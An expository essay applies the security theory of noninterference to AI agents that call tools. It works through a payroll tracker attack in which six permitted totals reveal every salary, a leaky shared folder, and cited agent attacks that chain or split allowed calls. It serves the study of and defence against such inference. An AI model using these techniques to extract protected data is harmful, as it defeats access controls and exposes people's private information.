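# Noninterference as a test of what a tool-using AI agent can infer from permitted outputs

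## Tool-using agents, restricted facts and observers

Noninterference is a computer security condition that a system meets, for a particular observer, when nothing anyone does with protected data changes what that observer sees. Joseph Goguen and José Meseguer set it out in 1982, and according to SRI, the research institute behind the work, it later gave military rules on classified data a formal basis. The same concern arises again with AI agents, which are language models that call software tools, read the results and choose what to call next. An agent can have permission for every call it makes and still obtain a fact that nobody meant it to have.

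Suppose a company gives its human resources agent a payroll tool. The agent may ask the tool for the total salary of any group of four or more people. It may not ask for anyone's individual salary. One department has five people, and these are their salaries in thousands:

| Ann | Bo | Cy | Dee | Eve |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 70 | 75 | 80 | 90 | 95 |

Five people make 31 possible groups. The tool answers for six of them, the five groups of four and the whole department, and refuses the other 25. Whoever wrote the rule presumably thought that a total over four people hides each person's value, which is true of a single total.

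*The Tracker*, a 1979 paper by Denning, Denning and Schwartz on databases that release only statistics, reported the same assumption among many users and designers, who believed individual records would stay confidential as long as the query program refused to answer about very small groups. The paper showed that this belief is wrong for almost all such databases. It used the word "compromise" for cases where a questioner deduces, from the answers to one or more queries, confidential information that the questioner did not have before. Learning that Dee earns 90 would count, and so would learning only that Dee does not earn 70. The HR tool has an obvious weakness of this kind, since the rule about group size does not stop an agent from requesting two permitted totals and subtracting one from the other.

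### The agent loop

An agent is a language model inside a loop. *Unrolling the Codex agent loop* (Bolin, 2026) describes this loop in OpenAI's coding agent. The program around the model assembles a prompt from the user's request, standing instructions and a list of the available tools, then sends it to the model. The model replies with either a final answer for the user or a tool call, a structured message that names a tool and fills in its arguments (here, "group total" and the names Ann, Bo, Cy and Dee). After a tool call, the program runs the tool, adds the output to the end of the prompt and queries the model again. The loop continues until the model gives a final answer.

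A permission check usually comes after the model requests a tool call and before the tool runs. In one pass through the loop, the HR agent's model reads its context, which is everything in the prompt so far, and proposes a call. The check allows or blocks the call. The result enters the context, and the model's next proposed call depends on that result and everything before it.

An agent's context accumulates as it works. In Codex, each new prompt within a turn begins with the whole of the previous one, and a single turn can include hundreds of tool calls. According to Anthropic's documentation for its Agent SDK, a toolkit for building agents on its Claude models, context also carries over between turns in a session, and resuming an old session restores its full context. Both systems summarize older material once the context grows too long, but a summary that keeps the useful findings lets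 the agent continue reasoning from them, so summarizing is not a reliable way to remove a salary total from the context.

When the SDK denies a call, a rejection message enters the model's context in place of the tool's output, and the model typically tries something else or reports that it could not proceed. In the HR case, the refusal reveals nothing about pay because it depends only on the number of names in the request. If the tool instead refused whenever a total exceeded 330, every refusal would reveal something about the salaries.

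### What a check on one call can see

*Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* (Surapani, Kakitapelli and colleagues, 2026), a review of 89 sources, says that the model proposes a tool call and a separate part of the system has to authorize it. *The Claws in Plain Sight* (2026) distinguishes a call that fits the tool's required format from one whose operation and contents are acceptable for the task, the purpose and the destination. The authorization check is there to establish that the call is acceptable, because a correctly formatted call may still not be permitted.

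Anthropic's toolkit shows what such checks look like in practice. Each call passes through up to six steps: the developer's custom code (a "hook"), rules that deny, rules that require confirmation, a general permission mode, rules that allow, and a developer-supplied function for calls that the earlier steps haven't decided. A typical rule matches a tool's name and the form of its arguments, for instance any shell command that starts with "npm". The rules check only the current call, though a developer could write a hook that keeps a record of earlier ones.

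The payroll tool's check only counts the names in a request and allows the call if there are four or more. It does not use earlier requests, so it gives the same result for the total of Ann, Bo, Cy and Dee whether that is the agent's first request or its sixth.

Giving the check a complete log would not be enough, because someone still has to work out what the logged results reveal together. That takes a little arithmetic for five salaries, but for emails, tickets and calendar entries it takes a judgment about what a reader could conclude from the combination, which is much harder to write as a rule. A check that runs before the tool does also cannot compare the current call's result with earlier ones, because that result is not yet available.

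Surapani and colleagues compare six places to put the check and find a trade-off between information and control. A check close to the model has more information about the task but less control over what happens, since a call may reach the tool by another route. Close to the data, the check has firm control, but often the only information available is whose credentials came with the request. They want checks that also take account of the agent's earlier actions, such as reading a sensitive file before sending an email, since a policy would not forbid either action by itself.

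None of this requires an attacker. *Securing Multi-Tool AI Agent Chains With Dynamic, Real-Time Compositional Policies* (2026) describes the danger as arising when a sequence of individually authorized calls gives the agent more than any one policy was meant to grant. In *Authorization Propagation in Multi-Agent AI Systems*, Tallam (2026) gives an example in which one agent retrieves dataset X, another retrieves dataset Y, and a third combines them into an answer for the user. Even if both retrievals are permitted, it is still an open question whether X and Y together reveal something that neither reveals alone. Tallam argues that this question would remain even if engineers completely solved prompt injection, in which an attacker hides instructions in content that an agent reads.

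In *Local Allow, Global Deny*, Pandey, Jain and colleagues (2026) ran a live agent on an open-weights model. In 22 of 60 runs, the agent broke the user's consent policy through steps that each passed their own check. A guard that checked only whether each action fitted the user's intent made no measurable difference, but one that checked the steps in combination eliminated these violations. In a separate offline audit, Claude Sonnet 4.6 resisted every kind of failure they tried, which they attribute to the model's good behavior because no monitor had caught anything.

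Tallam cites a 71% success rate across 14 business scenarios for an attack that splits a request into harmless-looking subtasks. The attack uses four mechanisms, only one of which is pooling identifying details, so the figure does not measure how often piecing facts together succeeds.

### High, low and restricted

The older theory's vocabulary carries over to agents fairly well. In Goguen and Meseguer's model, as *A Temporal Logic for Hyperproperties* (2013) restates it, users issue commands to a machine, and a function specifies what each user can observe. An observer is anyone who sees some of a system's outputs and must not learn protected data from them. The observer's *view* is everything the observer sees during a run. If the HR agent is the observer, its view includes the user's request, every total and every refusal.

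*High* data are data the policy protects from the observer, and *low* data are data the observer may see. The labels depend on who the observer is. For example, Dee's salary is high for the HR agent and low for the clerk who runs the payroll. A *protected input* is any data or action the policy marks high, which includes the five salaries and the clerk's act of changing one of them.

A *restricted fact* is a statement that the observer must not learn, whether or not anyone has stored it. "Dee earns 90" is stored in the payroll table. Surapani and colleagues describe a personal assistant that combines a calendar, location data, email and contacts, and infers a relationship between people that no single tool disclosed. No file contains that fact, so an administrator has nothing to mark high. A company can therefore label all its data carefully and still not cover everything it wants to keep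 from an observer.

A *permitted output* is a tool result or message that passes the permission check applied to it by itself. All six totals that the HR tool will give out are permitted outputs, even though the tool computes each of them from protected inputs.

### Where the observer stands

In the HR case, the agent is the observer, and the tools and the data behind them are the system. The concern is what the tools return into the agent's context.

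Often the agent instead has permission to read the high data, because it needs them to do its job, and so it is part of the system. The observer is then somebody outside who sees what the agent produces, such as the user reading its answer, the recipient of an email it sends, or a website that receives its search query. *ToolMinimize* (2026) adds some less obvious observers: tool operators who run the tool correctly but keep and analyze the arguments they receive, people watching network traffic, and aggregators who combine data from several calls in one session. In *How Much Can Tool Calls Reveal About You?* (2026), which tests how well a program can infer invented users' profiles from recorded tool calls, the observer is whoever holds the logs. A filter on the agent's final answer does not limit what an observer can learn by reading its queries. In *Agents That Know Too Much* (2026), a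 survey of privacy in agents, Lahjouji and Colaco argue that the key distinction is whether an observer sees only the final answer or also the channels in between, such as the agent's queries, tool arguments, memory and messages to other agents.

The same tools can be safe or unsafe depending on who the observer is. Pandey and colleagues use the example of a scheduling assistant that can read its owner's calendar and send messages. If the owner lets the assistant read the whole calendar and the assistant is the observer, nothing is high (restricted), so it cannot learn anything improperly. The observer could instead be the person who receives the proposed meeting times. The owner has agreed to show this person which slots are free, but not why the others are busy. Suppose the assistant offers Tuesday when Monday's busy block is an ordinary meeting, and Thursday when the same block is a confidential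 interview. Both slots are free and either message would pass a check, but what the recipient sees depends on a reason the owner wanted to keep private.

A set of tools can also be safe with employees as the observers but unsafe with the agent as the observer. If the HR agent has a second tool that posts a fixed notice, "salary review complete", on the staff page, and posts it once at five o'clock whatever it has found, employees who read only that page see the same words at the same time no matter what anyone earns. The agent, however, can collect all six totals.

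An auditor therefore cannot tell whether a list of tools is safe without also knowing who the observer is. There may well be several observers, since the HR agent observes the payroll tool and a manager observes the HR agent. Keeping Dee's salary from the agent also keeps it from a manager whose only source is the agent, however the agent behaves. But some jobs require the agent to have the data, and protection then depends on what the agent does with it. The attack in *The Claws in Plain Sight* exploits this by getting agents to put information they may legitimately read into tool-call arguments where it does not belong.

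### Influence and inference

Noninterference is a condition on influence, meaning whether anything in an observer's view depends on protected data, whoever the observer is. The HR company is more worried about inference, meaning whether the observer can work out a restricted fact from what it has permission to see. Inference from permitted pieces is usually known as the aggregation problem.

Noninterference is easy to confuse with inference control, the problem of "preventing inference of unauthorized information by combining authorized information". Goguen and Meseguer, who invented noninterference, discussed both this problem and a technique for verifying noninterference in *Unwinding and Inference Control* (1984). They wrote that the two topics were not closely related.

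In the payroll example, the influence question is easy to answer. Raising Cy's salary by 5 raises every total that includes Cy by 5, so the first answer the agent receives already depends on protected data. Whether the agent can infer Dee's salary of 90 from the totals is a separate question, and the answer depends on which totals it asks for and what it already knows.

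## Goguen and Meseguer's condition

Before 1982, formal definitions of computer security were mostly about who may read or write which file. The most influential was the model that D. E. Bell and L. J. LaPadula developed in the 1970s for multilevel security, the scheme governments use for classified documents. Each document has a classification (unclassified, confidential, secret or top secret) and each person has a clearance on the same scale. Information may move up the scale but not down. Bell and LaPadula turned this into two rules for programs and files. A program may read a file only if its clearance is at least as high as the file's classification. It may write to a file only if the file's classification is at least as high as the program's clearance. Without the rule on writing, a program with a secret clearance could copy a secret file into an unclassified one.

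A system can enforce these rules one request at a time, much as permission checks do for an agent's tool calls. Rushby (1992), in *Noninterference, Transitivity, and Channel-Control Security Policies*, objected that such a definition describes a mechanism, so it gives no guidance when the mechanism is inadequate. Rushby added that it is easy to build systems that follow the letter of the rules but are obviously insecure.

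Under Bell and LaPadula's "Basic Security Theorem", a system that starts in a secure state stays secure if no step adds or keeps an access that breaks the rules. McLean showed how little this guarantees in *A Comment on the "Basic Security Theorem" of Bell and LaPadula* (1985). He reversed the rule on writing, so that programs could write only to files at or below their own level, and proved the same theorem for the reversed system, even though its programs may copy secrets into unclassified files. The theorem holds for almost any property that can be checked state by state, so it is no evidence that the property deserves to be called security. In *Reasoning About Security Models* (1987), McLean also argued that no adequate definition of a secure system can rest solely on the notion of a secure state.

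Bell (1988), in *Concerning "Modeling" of Computer Security*, defended the Bell-LaPadula model by replying that one recent criticism had confused a model in the engineering sense, an abstraction for studying a problem, with a model in the logical sense, an interpretation of a formal theory. According to Rushby, proponents also answered that an implementation has to be a "faithful representation" of the model, but they never formally defined that phrase. Rushby attributed the model's weaknesses to two omissions. Bell and LaPadula did not define "read" and "write", so someone could swap the two and still satisfy the rules. They also left out the system's internal records, such as the table of who has access to what, and information can leak through those records without anyone reading a forbidden file.

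*Security Policies and Security Models* (Goguen and Meseguer, 1982) defines security in terms of what users can see, without referring to files, reading or writing. It separates the policy, which sets out what a system must prevent, from the model, which describes what the system does. A policy is a set of statements that one group of users does not interfere with another. Each statement is true when whatever the first group does with certain commands "has no effect on what the second group of users can see".

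### The machine

Rushby's notation is easier to follow than the original, and people who verify real systems still use it. The system is a machine with a set of states, one of which, s₀, is the initial state. Users submit actions, which can be any kind of command or input. Two functions describe the effect of an action:

- step(s, a) is the next state when action a happens in state s.
- output(s, a) is the result that the machine returns for action a in state s.

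The machine is deterministic, so the same action in the same state always has the same effect and the same output. The function run extends step to sequences of actions. If α is such a sequence, run(s, α) is the state the machine reaches by starting in s and performing the actions in α in order.

Every action a comes from a *domain*, written dom(a). A domain could be one person, one agent or everybody with the same clearance. The policy is a relation between domains, where u → v means that u may interfere with v and u ↛ v means that it may not. Every domain may interfere with itself. In the simplest case there are two domains, high (H) and low (L), with L → H and H ↛ L. High users may see the effects of low users' actions, but low users must not see any effect of high users' actions.

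Multilevel security fits this format. For any two levels, Goguen and Meseguer require that users at or above the higher level do not interfere with users at or below the lower one. They call a group "invisible" if it does not interfere with anyone outside it, because its members can observe outsiders without being observed by them. In Rushby's notation, u → v holds exactly when v's clearance is at least as high as u's.

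A multilevel policy is transitive, meaning that if u → v and v → w, then u → w. Rushby proved the converse, that every transitive policy is a multilevel policy for some choice of clearances. The proof groups domains that may interfere with each other into classes, then treats the classes as levels. Rushby also argued that the 1982 condition makes sense only for transitive policies, and that policies that let high data out through an approved intermediary need a different version.

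### Purging a history

The condition compares what happened with what would have happened if the high users had done nothing. To state it, Rushby defines a function called purge. For a sequence α and a domain v, purge(α, v) is what remains of α after deleting every action whose domain may not interfere with v. Going through the sequence from the front:

- If α is empty, purge(α, v) is empty.
- If α begins with an action a and dom(a) → v, keep a and purge the rest.
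- If α begins with an action a and dom(a) ↛ v, drop a and purge the rest.

With only two domains, purge(α, L) is the history with the high users' actions removed and the low users' actions kept in their original order.

One more abbreviation is useful. Let test(α, a) be the output of action a after the machine has started in s₀ and performed α, which is output(run(s₀, α), a). A system is secure for the policy if

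test(α, a) = test(purge(α, dom(a)), a)

The condition requires that whenever a domain performs an action, the output is the same as it would have been if no forbidden domain had ever acted. Rushby describes the action a as an experiment in which the domain uses the output to learn something about the history α. If any such experiment gives different outputs for the full history and the purged one, a forbidden domain has interfered.

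The equation has to hold for every sequence α and every action a, so a single sequence that breaks it makes the system insecure, however long or unlikely that sequence is. Passing many tests doesn't show that a system is secure, because an untested sequence might break the equation.

The equation compares only the last output, while an agent's context retains many earlier ones. Comparing those as well would not change the condition, because each resulted from an action after a shorter history, which the equation also covers. Rushby notes that definitions which compare all the outputs an observer has seen are equivalent to this one.

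Protected data enter the model through actions. In the payroll example, a clerk typed Dee's salary into the table, and that entry is a high action. Purging the history deletes the entry, which changes any total that included Dee's salary.

### The merger memo

Suppose a lawyer in domain H and an AI agent in domain L share a company folder, with L → H and H ↛ L. Both can create files by name, but the agent cannot open or list the lawyer's files. The folder has a single list of names for all users, and a request to create a file returns either "created" or "name in use".

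The agent creates a file called agenda. The lawyer then creates one called merger-memo. Finally the agent, which happens to be writing notes on a merger, tries to create a file with the same name as the lawyer's. The table compares this history with the purged one.

| Action | Reply in the full history | Reply in the purged history |
|---|---|---|
| Agent creates agenda | created | created |
| Lawyer creates merger-memo | created (only the lawyer sees this) | (deleted) |
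| Agent creates merger-memo | name in use | created |

Here, α is the first two actions and a is the last one. The domain of a is L, so purge(α, L) deletes the lawyer's action and leaves the agent's first action. test(α, a) is "name in use", and test(purge(α, L), a) is "created". These outputs differ, so the folder fails the condition.

The agent never opened the lawyer's file, and the lawyer wrote only to a high file, so Bell and LaPadula's rules both hold. The information leaked through the list of names, one of the internal records that the access rules don't cover. Unlike the payroll tool's refusals, this refusal depends on what a high user did.

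Ryan, in *Mathematical Models of Computer Security*, uses nearly the same example against Bell and LaPadula's model. A low user asks to create a file, and the system replies that a file of that name already exists. Ryan concedes that this leak may not be very useful as it stands, but a malicious program running at the high level could use it to send messages. For example, it could send a low program one bit for each name on a prearranged list by creating or not creating a file with that name.

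The first example in the 1982 paper rules out this kind of reply. If the commands that create, change or delete a file must not interfere with a certain user, and the file did not exist at the start, then the system must keep reporting to that user that the file doesn't exist, whatever anyone has done with those commands.

*Nickel*, by Sigurbjarnarson, Nelson and colleagues, describes several leaks of the same sort in operating systems. A system might number new threads (separate strands of a running program) in order. A low thread creates one and receives number 3, a high thread creates one and receives 4, and the low thread creates another and receives 5. If the high thread's action were purged, the low thread would receive 3 and 4. A high thread can therefore pass on any number x by creating x threads. In another example, a thread requests the status of a page of memory, and the system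 returns one error code if nobody is using the page and another if someone is using it and the thread may not see it. Both codes refuse access, but a low thread can infer from which one it receives whether a high thread has taken the page.

The fix for the folder is to give each domain its own list of names. The reply to the agent then depends only on names that the agent has used, so the agent sees "created" in both histories. The lawyer may see both files called merger-memo, so the folder has to show them differently, perhaps with the owner next to the name. Ryan calls this fix poly-instantiation. Sigurbjarnarson and colleagues recommend it for thread numbers and memory pages as well as files.

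### The unwinding theorem

The fix deals with one sequence of three actions, but the condition covers all of the infinitely many possible sequences. Goguen and Meseguer's 1984 theorem makes it possible to check single actions instead of whole histories. Rushby's version works as follows.

For each domain u, decide which states *look alike* to u. The choice is free, except that it has to behave like sameness: every state looks like itself, if s looks like t then t looks like s, and if s looks like t and t looks like r then s looks like r. The theorem is that a system is secure if it meets three conditions for all states s and t, all actions a and all domains u:

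- *Output consistency*: if s and t look alike to dom(a), then output(s, a) = output(t, a).
- *Step consistency*: if s and t look alike to u, then step(s, a) and step(t, a) look alike to u.
- *Local respect*: if dom(a) ↛ u, then s and step(s, a) look alike to u.

Output consistency means that if two states look alike to a domain, the domain gets the same outputs in both. Step consistency means that if two states look alike to a domain, they still look alike to it after the same action is performed in both. Local respect means that an action doesn't change how the state looks to any domain it is not allowed to interfere with.

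The proof uses two copies of the machine, one running the full history α and the other running purge(α, u). Induction on the length of α shows that if the copies start in states s and t that look alike to u, they also finish in states that look alike to u.

If α is empty, neither copy does anything, so the claim is true by assumption. Suppose the claim is true for every sequence of length n and every pair of starting states that look alike to u. Take a sequence of length n + 1 that starts with the action a.

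If dom(a) → u, purge keeps a, so both copies perform it. By step consistency, step(s, a) and step(t, a) look alike to u. The claim for length n covers the remaining n actions.

If dom(a) ↛ u, purge deletes a. The copy with the full history performs it and moves to step(s, a), while the other copy stays at t. By local respect, step(s, a) looks like s to u, and s looks like t to u, so step(s, a) looks like t to u. Again n actions remain, and the claim for length n covers them.

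To derive the condition from this, we start both copies in s₀ and let u be the domain that will perform the test action. After one copy runs the full history and the other runs the purged history, their states look alike to u. By output consistency, u then receives the same output from both copies, as the condition requires. Young's *Proof of Non-Interference Unwinding Theorem* gives a shorter version of the proof that compares the parts of the state visible to each user instead of outputs, so it needs only step consistency and local respect.

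### Checking the folder

In the repaired folder, a state consists of two lists, the agent's names and the lawyer's names. Two states look alike to the agent if the agent's list is the same in each, and to the lawyer if both lists are the same.

Output consistency holds because the reply to the agent depends only on the agent's list and the reply to the lawyer depends only on the lawyer's list. Step consistency holds for the agent because if two states have the same agent's list, they still do after either user creates a file. A file the agent creates adds the same name to that list in both states, and a file the lawyer creates leaves it unchanged. Two states that look alike to the lawyer have both lists in common, and they still do after any action. Local respect matters only for H ↛ L, and it holds because the lawyer's actions never change the agent's list. Since all three conditions hold,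 the agent cannot learn anything about the lawyer's file names from any sequence of requests.

The original folder fails this check however we define which states look alike to the agent. If states look alike only when the whole shared list is the same, the lawyer's action changes what the agent sees, so local respect fails. If the names the lawyer created don't count, local respect holds, but the agent can get different replies in two states that look alike, so output consistency fails. Rushby proved that every secure system has a definition that meets all three conditions. Under it, two states look alike to u when no further sequence of actions would lead to different outputs for u.

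The repaired folder passes partly because the example is simple. If the company limited the folder to 1,000 files in total, the lawyer could fill it, and the agent's next request would get the reply "folder full". The lawyer's actions would then affect what the agent sees again. Sigurbjarnarson and colleagues list this as another common leak, and one of their remedies is a separate quota for each domain.

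Their framework uses a solver, a program that searches for values satisfying a set of logical formulas, to check a version of the three conditions automatically for every operation. When a check fails, the solver produces a counterexample with specific states and a specific operation. They verified two operating system kernels this way and reproduced three known leaks in a communication standard for aircraft electronics. Developers have to supply the look-alike relation, but a bad choice can't produce a false proof, because any relation that meets the conditions is sufficient. If a developer writes down the wrong policy, however, the solver will still confirm that the system meets it.

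The theorem also shows when access rules are sufficient. Rushby considers a machine whose state is a collection of storage locations, with a table of who may observe and who may alter each one. The table must match the machine's behavior, so that outputs and new values depend only on locations the acting domain may observe, and an action changes only locations its domain may alter. Under these assumptions, Bell and LaPadula's two rules guarantee noninterference for a multilevel policy. In the original folder, the shared list is a location that the lawyer alters and the agent in effect observes. An auditor who had put the list in the table would have found the problem using access rules alone. But people forget to list such locations, and the rules provide no way to detect the omission.

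### What the model takes as given

Goguen and Meseguer describe four stages for making a system secure: determining what the community of users needs, expressing those needs as a formal requirement, modeling the system, and verifying that the model meets the requirement. Only the last stage is purely mathematical, and the guarantee it provides depends on how well the other three are done.

The model has a set of named users and records which user submitted each action. Goguen and Meseguer explicitly set aside the problem of verifying users' identities. If an agent can act under the lawyer's login, those actions count as the lawyer's, and a proof about what the agent can see no longer describes its actual access.

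In the original version, a single output function determines what each user sees in each state, and Goguen and Meseguer assume that this function covers everything the system reveals to its users. For an agent, it would have to include tool results, refusals, error messages, lists of available tools and anything else that enters the context. A developer could easily leave something out. If they modeled the original folder but treated error messages as a technical detail, the proof would still succeed, but the agent would learn about the merger memo anyway.

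Ryan points out that the model also leaves out time. The repaired folder might take slightly longer to reply when the lawyer has many files, and an agent that measured the delay would learn something the proof does not cover. In other respects the assumptions are cautious. Ryan notes that the definition effectively gives hostile observers complete knowledge of the system's design and lets all the low users work together, and real observers will usually know less.

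Goguen and Meseguer write that users can presumably learn things outside the system, "but we do not attempt to describe that". If a colleague tells the agent about the merger memo by email, and the email system is not part of the model, the folder still satisfies the condition. Goguen and Meseguer also explicitly exclude the aggregation problem. The condition given here assumes that the policy stays the same throughout a run, though the 1982 paper has a separate version for permissions that change.

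### What verified systems prove

Several systems already have a proof of noninterference, and a developer might want to run an agent on top of one. In *Noninterference specifications for secure systems*, Nelson, Bornholt and colleagues examined eleven verified systems, including operating system kernels, a browser kernel and a file system. They found that "noninterference" refers to four different kinds of specification, often with small variations specific to each system.

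Four of the eleven prove noninterference in roughly the sense of this section, by comparing a full history with a purged one. Two prove nonleakage, a property of two runs that have the same sequence of actions but different starting states. If the starting states look alike to the observer and to everyone who may pass information to the observer along the way, the observer's final view must be the same in both runs. Nonleakage is meant to protect the data in the state. It does not hide that somebody performed an action, because both runs contain the same actions.

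One of these two is seL4, a small operating system kernel. The paper *seL4* presents the proof and reports that it applies to the kernel's actual 8,830 lines of C code. The proof assumes that the compiler, hardware, assembly code and boot code are correct, and it does not cover some covert channels.

The other five systems use unwinding conditions as the specification itself. Two of them require output consistency, local respect and a weaker form of step consistency that suits policies with approved releases of data. Three require only output consistency and step consistency. Nelson and colleagues show what omitting local respect can allow, using Komodo, which protects regions of memory called enclaves from the operating system that manages them. Komodo's original specification stops the operating system from overwriting an enclave's memory with data that the enclave may not see, but would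 allow the operating system to fill that memory with zeros. A later version of Komodo that includes local respect rules this out.

SFSCQ, the file system in the survey, is also in this group. *Proving confidentiality in a file system using DiskSec* (Ileri, Chajed and colleagues, 2018) presents SFSCQ's specification as a middle ground between strict information-flow control and the weaker permissions of ordinary file systems. The specification keeps the contents of files confidential, but not their existence or length.

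The original shared folder, with its single list of names, would meet a specification like this. Here, two states look alike to the agent when they have the same list of names and the agent's own files have the same contents. The replies "created" and "name in use" depend only on the list, so output consistency holds. Any request to create a file changes the list in the same way in both states, so step consistency holds too. Only local respect fails, and the specification doesn't include it. For many companies that would be fine, since file names are rarely secret. A company that wants to hide the existence of a merger memo from its agent would need a proof that includes local respect.

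## Influence and inference: what passing or failing the test shows

Goguen and Meseguer had good reason to distinguish inference from noninterference. The payroll tool fails noninterference with the first total it returns, but the agent can't infer anyone's pay from one total. Other systems satisfy noninterference and still let an agent infer something the company wanted to hide.

### What passing guarantees

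If a deterministic system satisfies noninterference, an agent cannot uncover a protected input by chaining calls. This holds even if the agent uses one reply to choose the next call, saves notes, reads them back and combines everything at the end. The guarantee covers every strategy a language model might come up with, so there is no need to list them all, which nobody could do.

The proof compares *paired runs*, two runs that differ only in protected data. Let the agent be the low domain L and, for simplicity, the only low user. Its starting context (the request, the standing instructions and the list of tools) is the same in both runs. Assume the agent is deterministic, so the same view always leads to the same next call. The high users can do anything, and their actions can differ between the two runs.

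The claim is that the agent's view is the same in both runs after any number of calls. Before the first call this is true because the starting contexts are the same. Now suppose it is true after k calls. The agent chooses its next call, a, from the same view in both runs, so a is the same too. Let α be everything that has happened so far in the first run, and β everything that has happened in the second. These histories may contain quite different high actions, but purging them leaves the same sequence, the agent's k calls in order. So purge(α, L) = purge(β, L), and applying the noninterference condition to each history gives

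test(α, a) = test(purge(α, L), a) = test(purge(β, L), a) = test(β, a)

The agent therefore gets the same reply to a in both runs, and its view is still the same after k + 1 calls. By induction, its view is the same after any number of calls.

Suppose the lawyer creates a file called merger-memo in the repaired folder in one run and creates nothing in the other. In both runs, the agent tries the name merger-memo, gets the reply "created", saves a note about it, reads the note back and picks another name to try. Saving and reading notes are calls like any other, so the proof covers them. If the agent then guesses whether the lawyer has created merger-memo, it makes the same guess in both runs and is wrong in one of them.

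The proof's only assumption about the agent is that it is deterministic, so using a much more capable model doesn't weaken the guarantee. A model that samples its words at random needs a condition stated in probabilities. But the guarantee depends on every reply. If one reply varies with the protected data, the agent's views can differ from that point on, and so can every later call.

### Facts that follow from low data

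The guarantee covers protected inputs, but a restricted fact may not be one of them. *The Sum Leaks More Than Its Parts* (Patil, Stengel-Eskin and Bansal, 2025) gives the example of a customer, John, who has bought a blood pressure monitor and a cholesterol test kit. One table links customer numbers to names, another links them to purchases, and a third contains insurance claims, which show no diagnosed heart condition for John. Anyone who combines the tables can infer that John is watching for an undiagnosed heart problem, although no table contains that fact.

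Suppose a pharmacy gives an agent its customers' names and purchases, both marked low, and keeps doctors' diagnoses in a separate system, marked high. The agent's tools never access the diagnoses, so adding, changing or deleting one doesn't affect any reply, and the setup satisfies noninterference. But if a customer buys what people with heart disease typically buy, the agent can infer the diagnosis anyway. Usually the inference is only probable, since the customer might be shopping for a relative. If the pharmacy sells some product only to people with a particular diagnosis, the inference is certain.

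The diagnosis influences the purchases here through its effect on the customer, not through the computer. The purge deletes the doctor's entry but keeps the shopping that followed from it, so the purged history would probably never have happened.

The pharmacy could mark purchases high as well, but then the agent could not use them to reorder stock or answer a question about a delivery unless the pharmacy approved exceptions. Somebody would also have to notice that purchases reveal diagnoses, which is easy for heart monitors and much harder for the thousands of other combinations in a shop's records.

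### Influence without inference

The agent can ask the payroll tool for the total of Ann's, Bo's, Cy's and Eve's salaries, and the reply is 320. Like every total, this one depends on protected data, but the agent can't work out Eve's salary from it alone. Suppose everyone knows that salaries at the company run from 60 to 100. Whatever Eve earns in that range, the other three salaries must add up to between 220 and 260, which is possible because three salaries in the range can add up to anything from 180 to 300.

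In *Inference Controls for Statistical Databases*, Denning and Schlorer explain that harmless-looking statistics contain "small vestiges of the data used to compute them", and that somebody who correlates enough of these statistics can infer sensitive data about an individual. The data therefore influence even the first total, whether or not anyone can infer an individual's data from it.

A system satisfies *nondeducibility* if, in every run, what the observer saw is compatible with every possible value of the protected input. In a deterministic system, noninterference implies nondeducibility, because the observer sees the same thing for every value of the protected input and so can't rule any of them out.

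A tool can fail noninterference even if an agent can't infer the secret from its output. Suppose a tool answers "yes" if Ann and Bo both got bonuses this year or neither did, and "no" otherwise. Changing whether Ann got a bonus changes the answer, so the tool fails noninterference. Yet neither answer reveals whether Ann got one.

Nondeducibility is easy to misapply. The company has to specify which input it wants to protect. With a total of 320, Eve could still earn any possible salary, but most lists of all five salaries are ruled out. The condition also has to hold in every run. If the same four people earned 395 in total, Eve would have to earn at least 95, because the other three can't earn more than 300 between them. So even a payroll tool that answered only one question would fail for some sets of salaries.

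Nondeducibility also ignores probability. An agent that began by treating every salary from 60 to 100 as equally likely should conclude from the 320 that Eve is more likely to earn 80 than 60, but the 320 doesn't rule out any of those salaries. The condition doesn't stop a high program from signaling to a low one by choosing its actions strategically, either. The pharmacy satisfies the condition for diagnoses because its computers would accept any diagnosis alongside any purchases. Some combinations are unlikely because of how people behave, which the model of the system leaves out.

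Influence and inference can therefore occur in any combination:

| | The agent can work out the restricted fact | The agent can't work it out |
|---|---|---|
| Replies depend on protected data | Payroll tool, all six totals: "Eve earns 95" | Payroll tool, one total: "Eve earns 95" |
| Replies don't depend on protected data | Pharmacy: "this customer has heart disease" | Repaired folder: "the lawyer has a file called merger-memo" |

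Noninterference distinguishes the two rows. Companies mostly care about the columns.

### The tracker attack

One more total exposes Eve's salary. The agent asks for the whole department and gets 410, then asks for everyone except Eve and gets 315. Both groups have at least four people, so both calls pass the check. Eve earns 410 − 315 = 95. Leaving out Dee, Cy, Bo and Ann in turn gives 320, 330, 335 and 340, and subtracting each from 410 gives their salaries too. Six permitted calls reveal the whole table. Every reply is correct and goes to an agent with permission to receive it, so encrypting the payroll data wouldn't help.

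Banning the department total wouldn't help either. The five totals for groups of four add up to 1,640, and each salary appears in four of them, so the agent can divide by 4 to get the department total, 410.

Denning and colleagues considered a stricter rule that refuses questions about very large groups as well as very small ones. In their example, a college has 12 employees, and its database answers a question only if between 2 and 10 people match the description. Dodd is the only female computer science professor, so the database refuses a direct question about her salary. But a questioner can ask for the total salary of all women ($90,000) and the total for all women except computer science professors ($75,000). The difference is Dodd's salary, $15,000. The second description is a *tracker*, a permitted query that helps answer a forbidden one.

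This attack requires some prior knowledge. A questioner who knew only that Dodd was a woman in computer science would not learn her salary this way, because two women fit that description and the answers don't show which of them earns what.

Denning and colleagues also found *general trackers*, which work for everyone in a database. In the college, "male" is a general tracker. The questioner first adds the total for men ($104,000) to the total for women ($90,000) and gets $194,000 for the whole college. The next two questions each cover a larger group that includes Dodd. "Men, plus any female computer science professor" matches eight people, who earn $119,000 in total. "Women, plus any female computer science professor" matches just the five women, who earn $90,000 in total. Together, these two totals count Dodd twice and everyone else once. Their sum is $209,000, and subtracting $194,000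 leaves Dodd's $15,000.

The same method, with a variant for groups that are too large, answers any question the database refuses, using at most four queries beyond the first two. If the database has n records and refuses groups smaller than k or larger than n − k, any description that matches between 2k and n − 2k people is a general tracker. Denning and colleagues concluded that severe limits on group size would make a database useless for statistics and still not protect individual records.

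### Auditing the history of questions

*Query auditing*, unlike a limit on group size, takes account of earlier questions. An auditing program refuses a question if the answer, combined with its earlier answers, would reveal a protected value.

For totals, this is linear algebra. Each answer is an equation in the unknown salaries, and the program refuses a new total if the enlarged set of equations would determine anybody's salary. With the payroll table, the number of totals an agent can get depends on the order of its questions. An agent that starts with the whole department gets 410 and no further totals, because the total for any group of four would expose the salary of the person left out. An agent that starts with groups of four can get the totals for four of the five such groups. Those four equations leave every salary undetermined, while adding either the fifth group's total or the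 whole department's would determine all of them.

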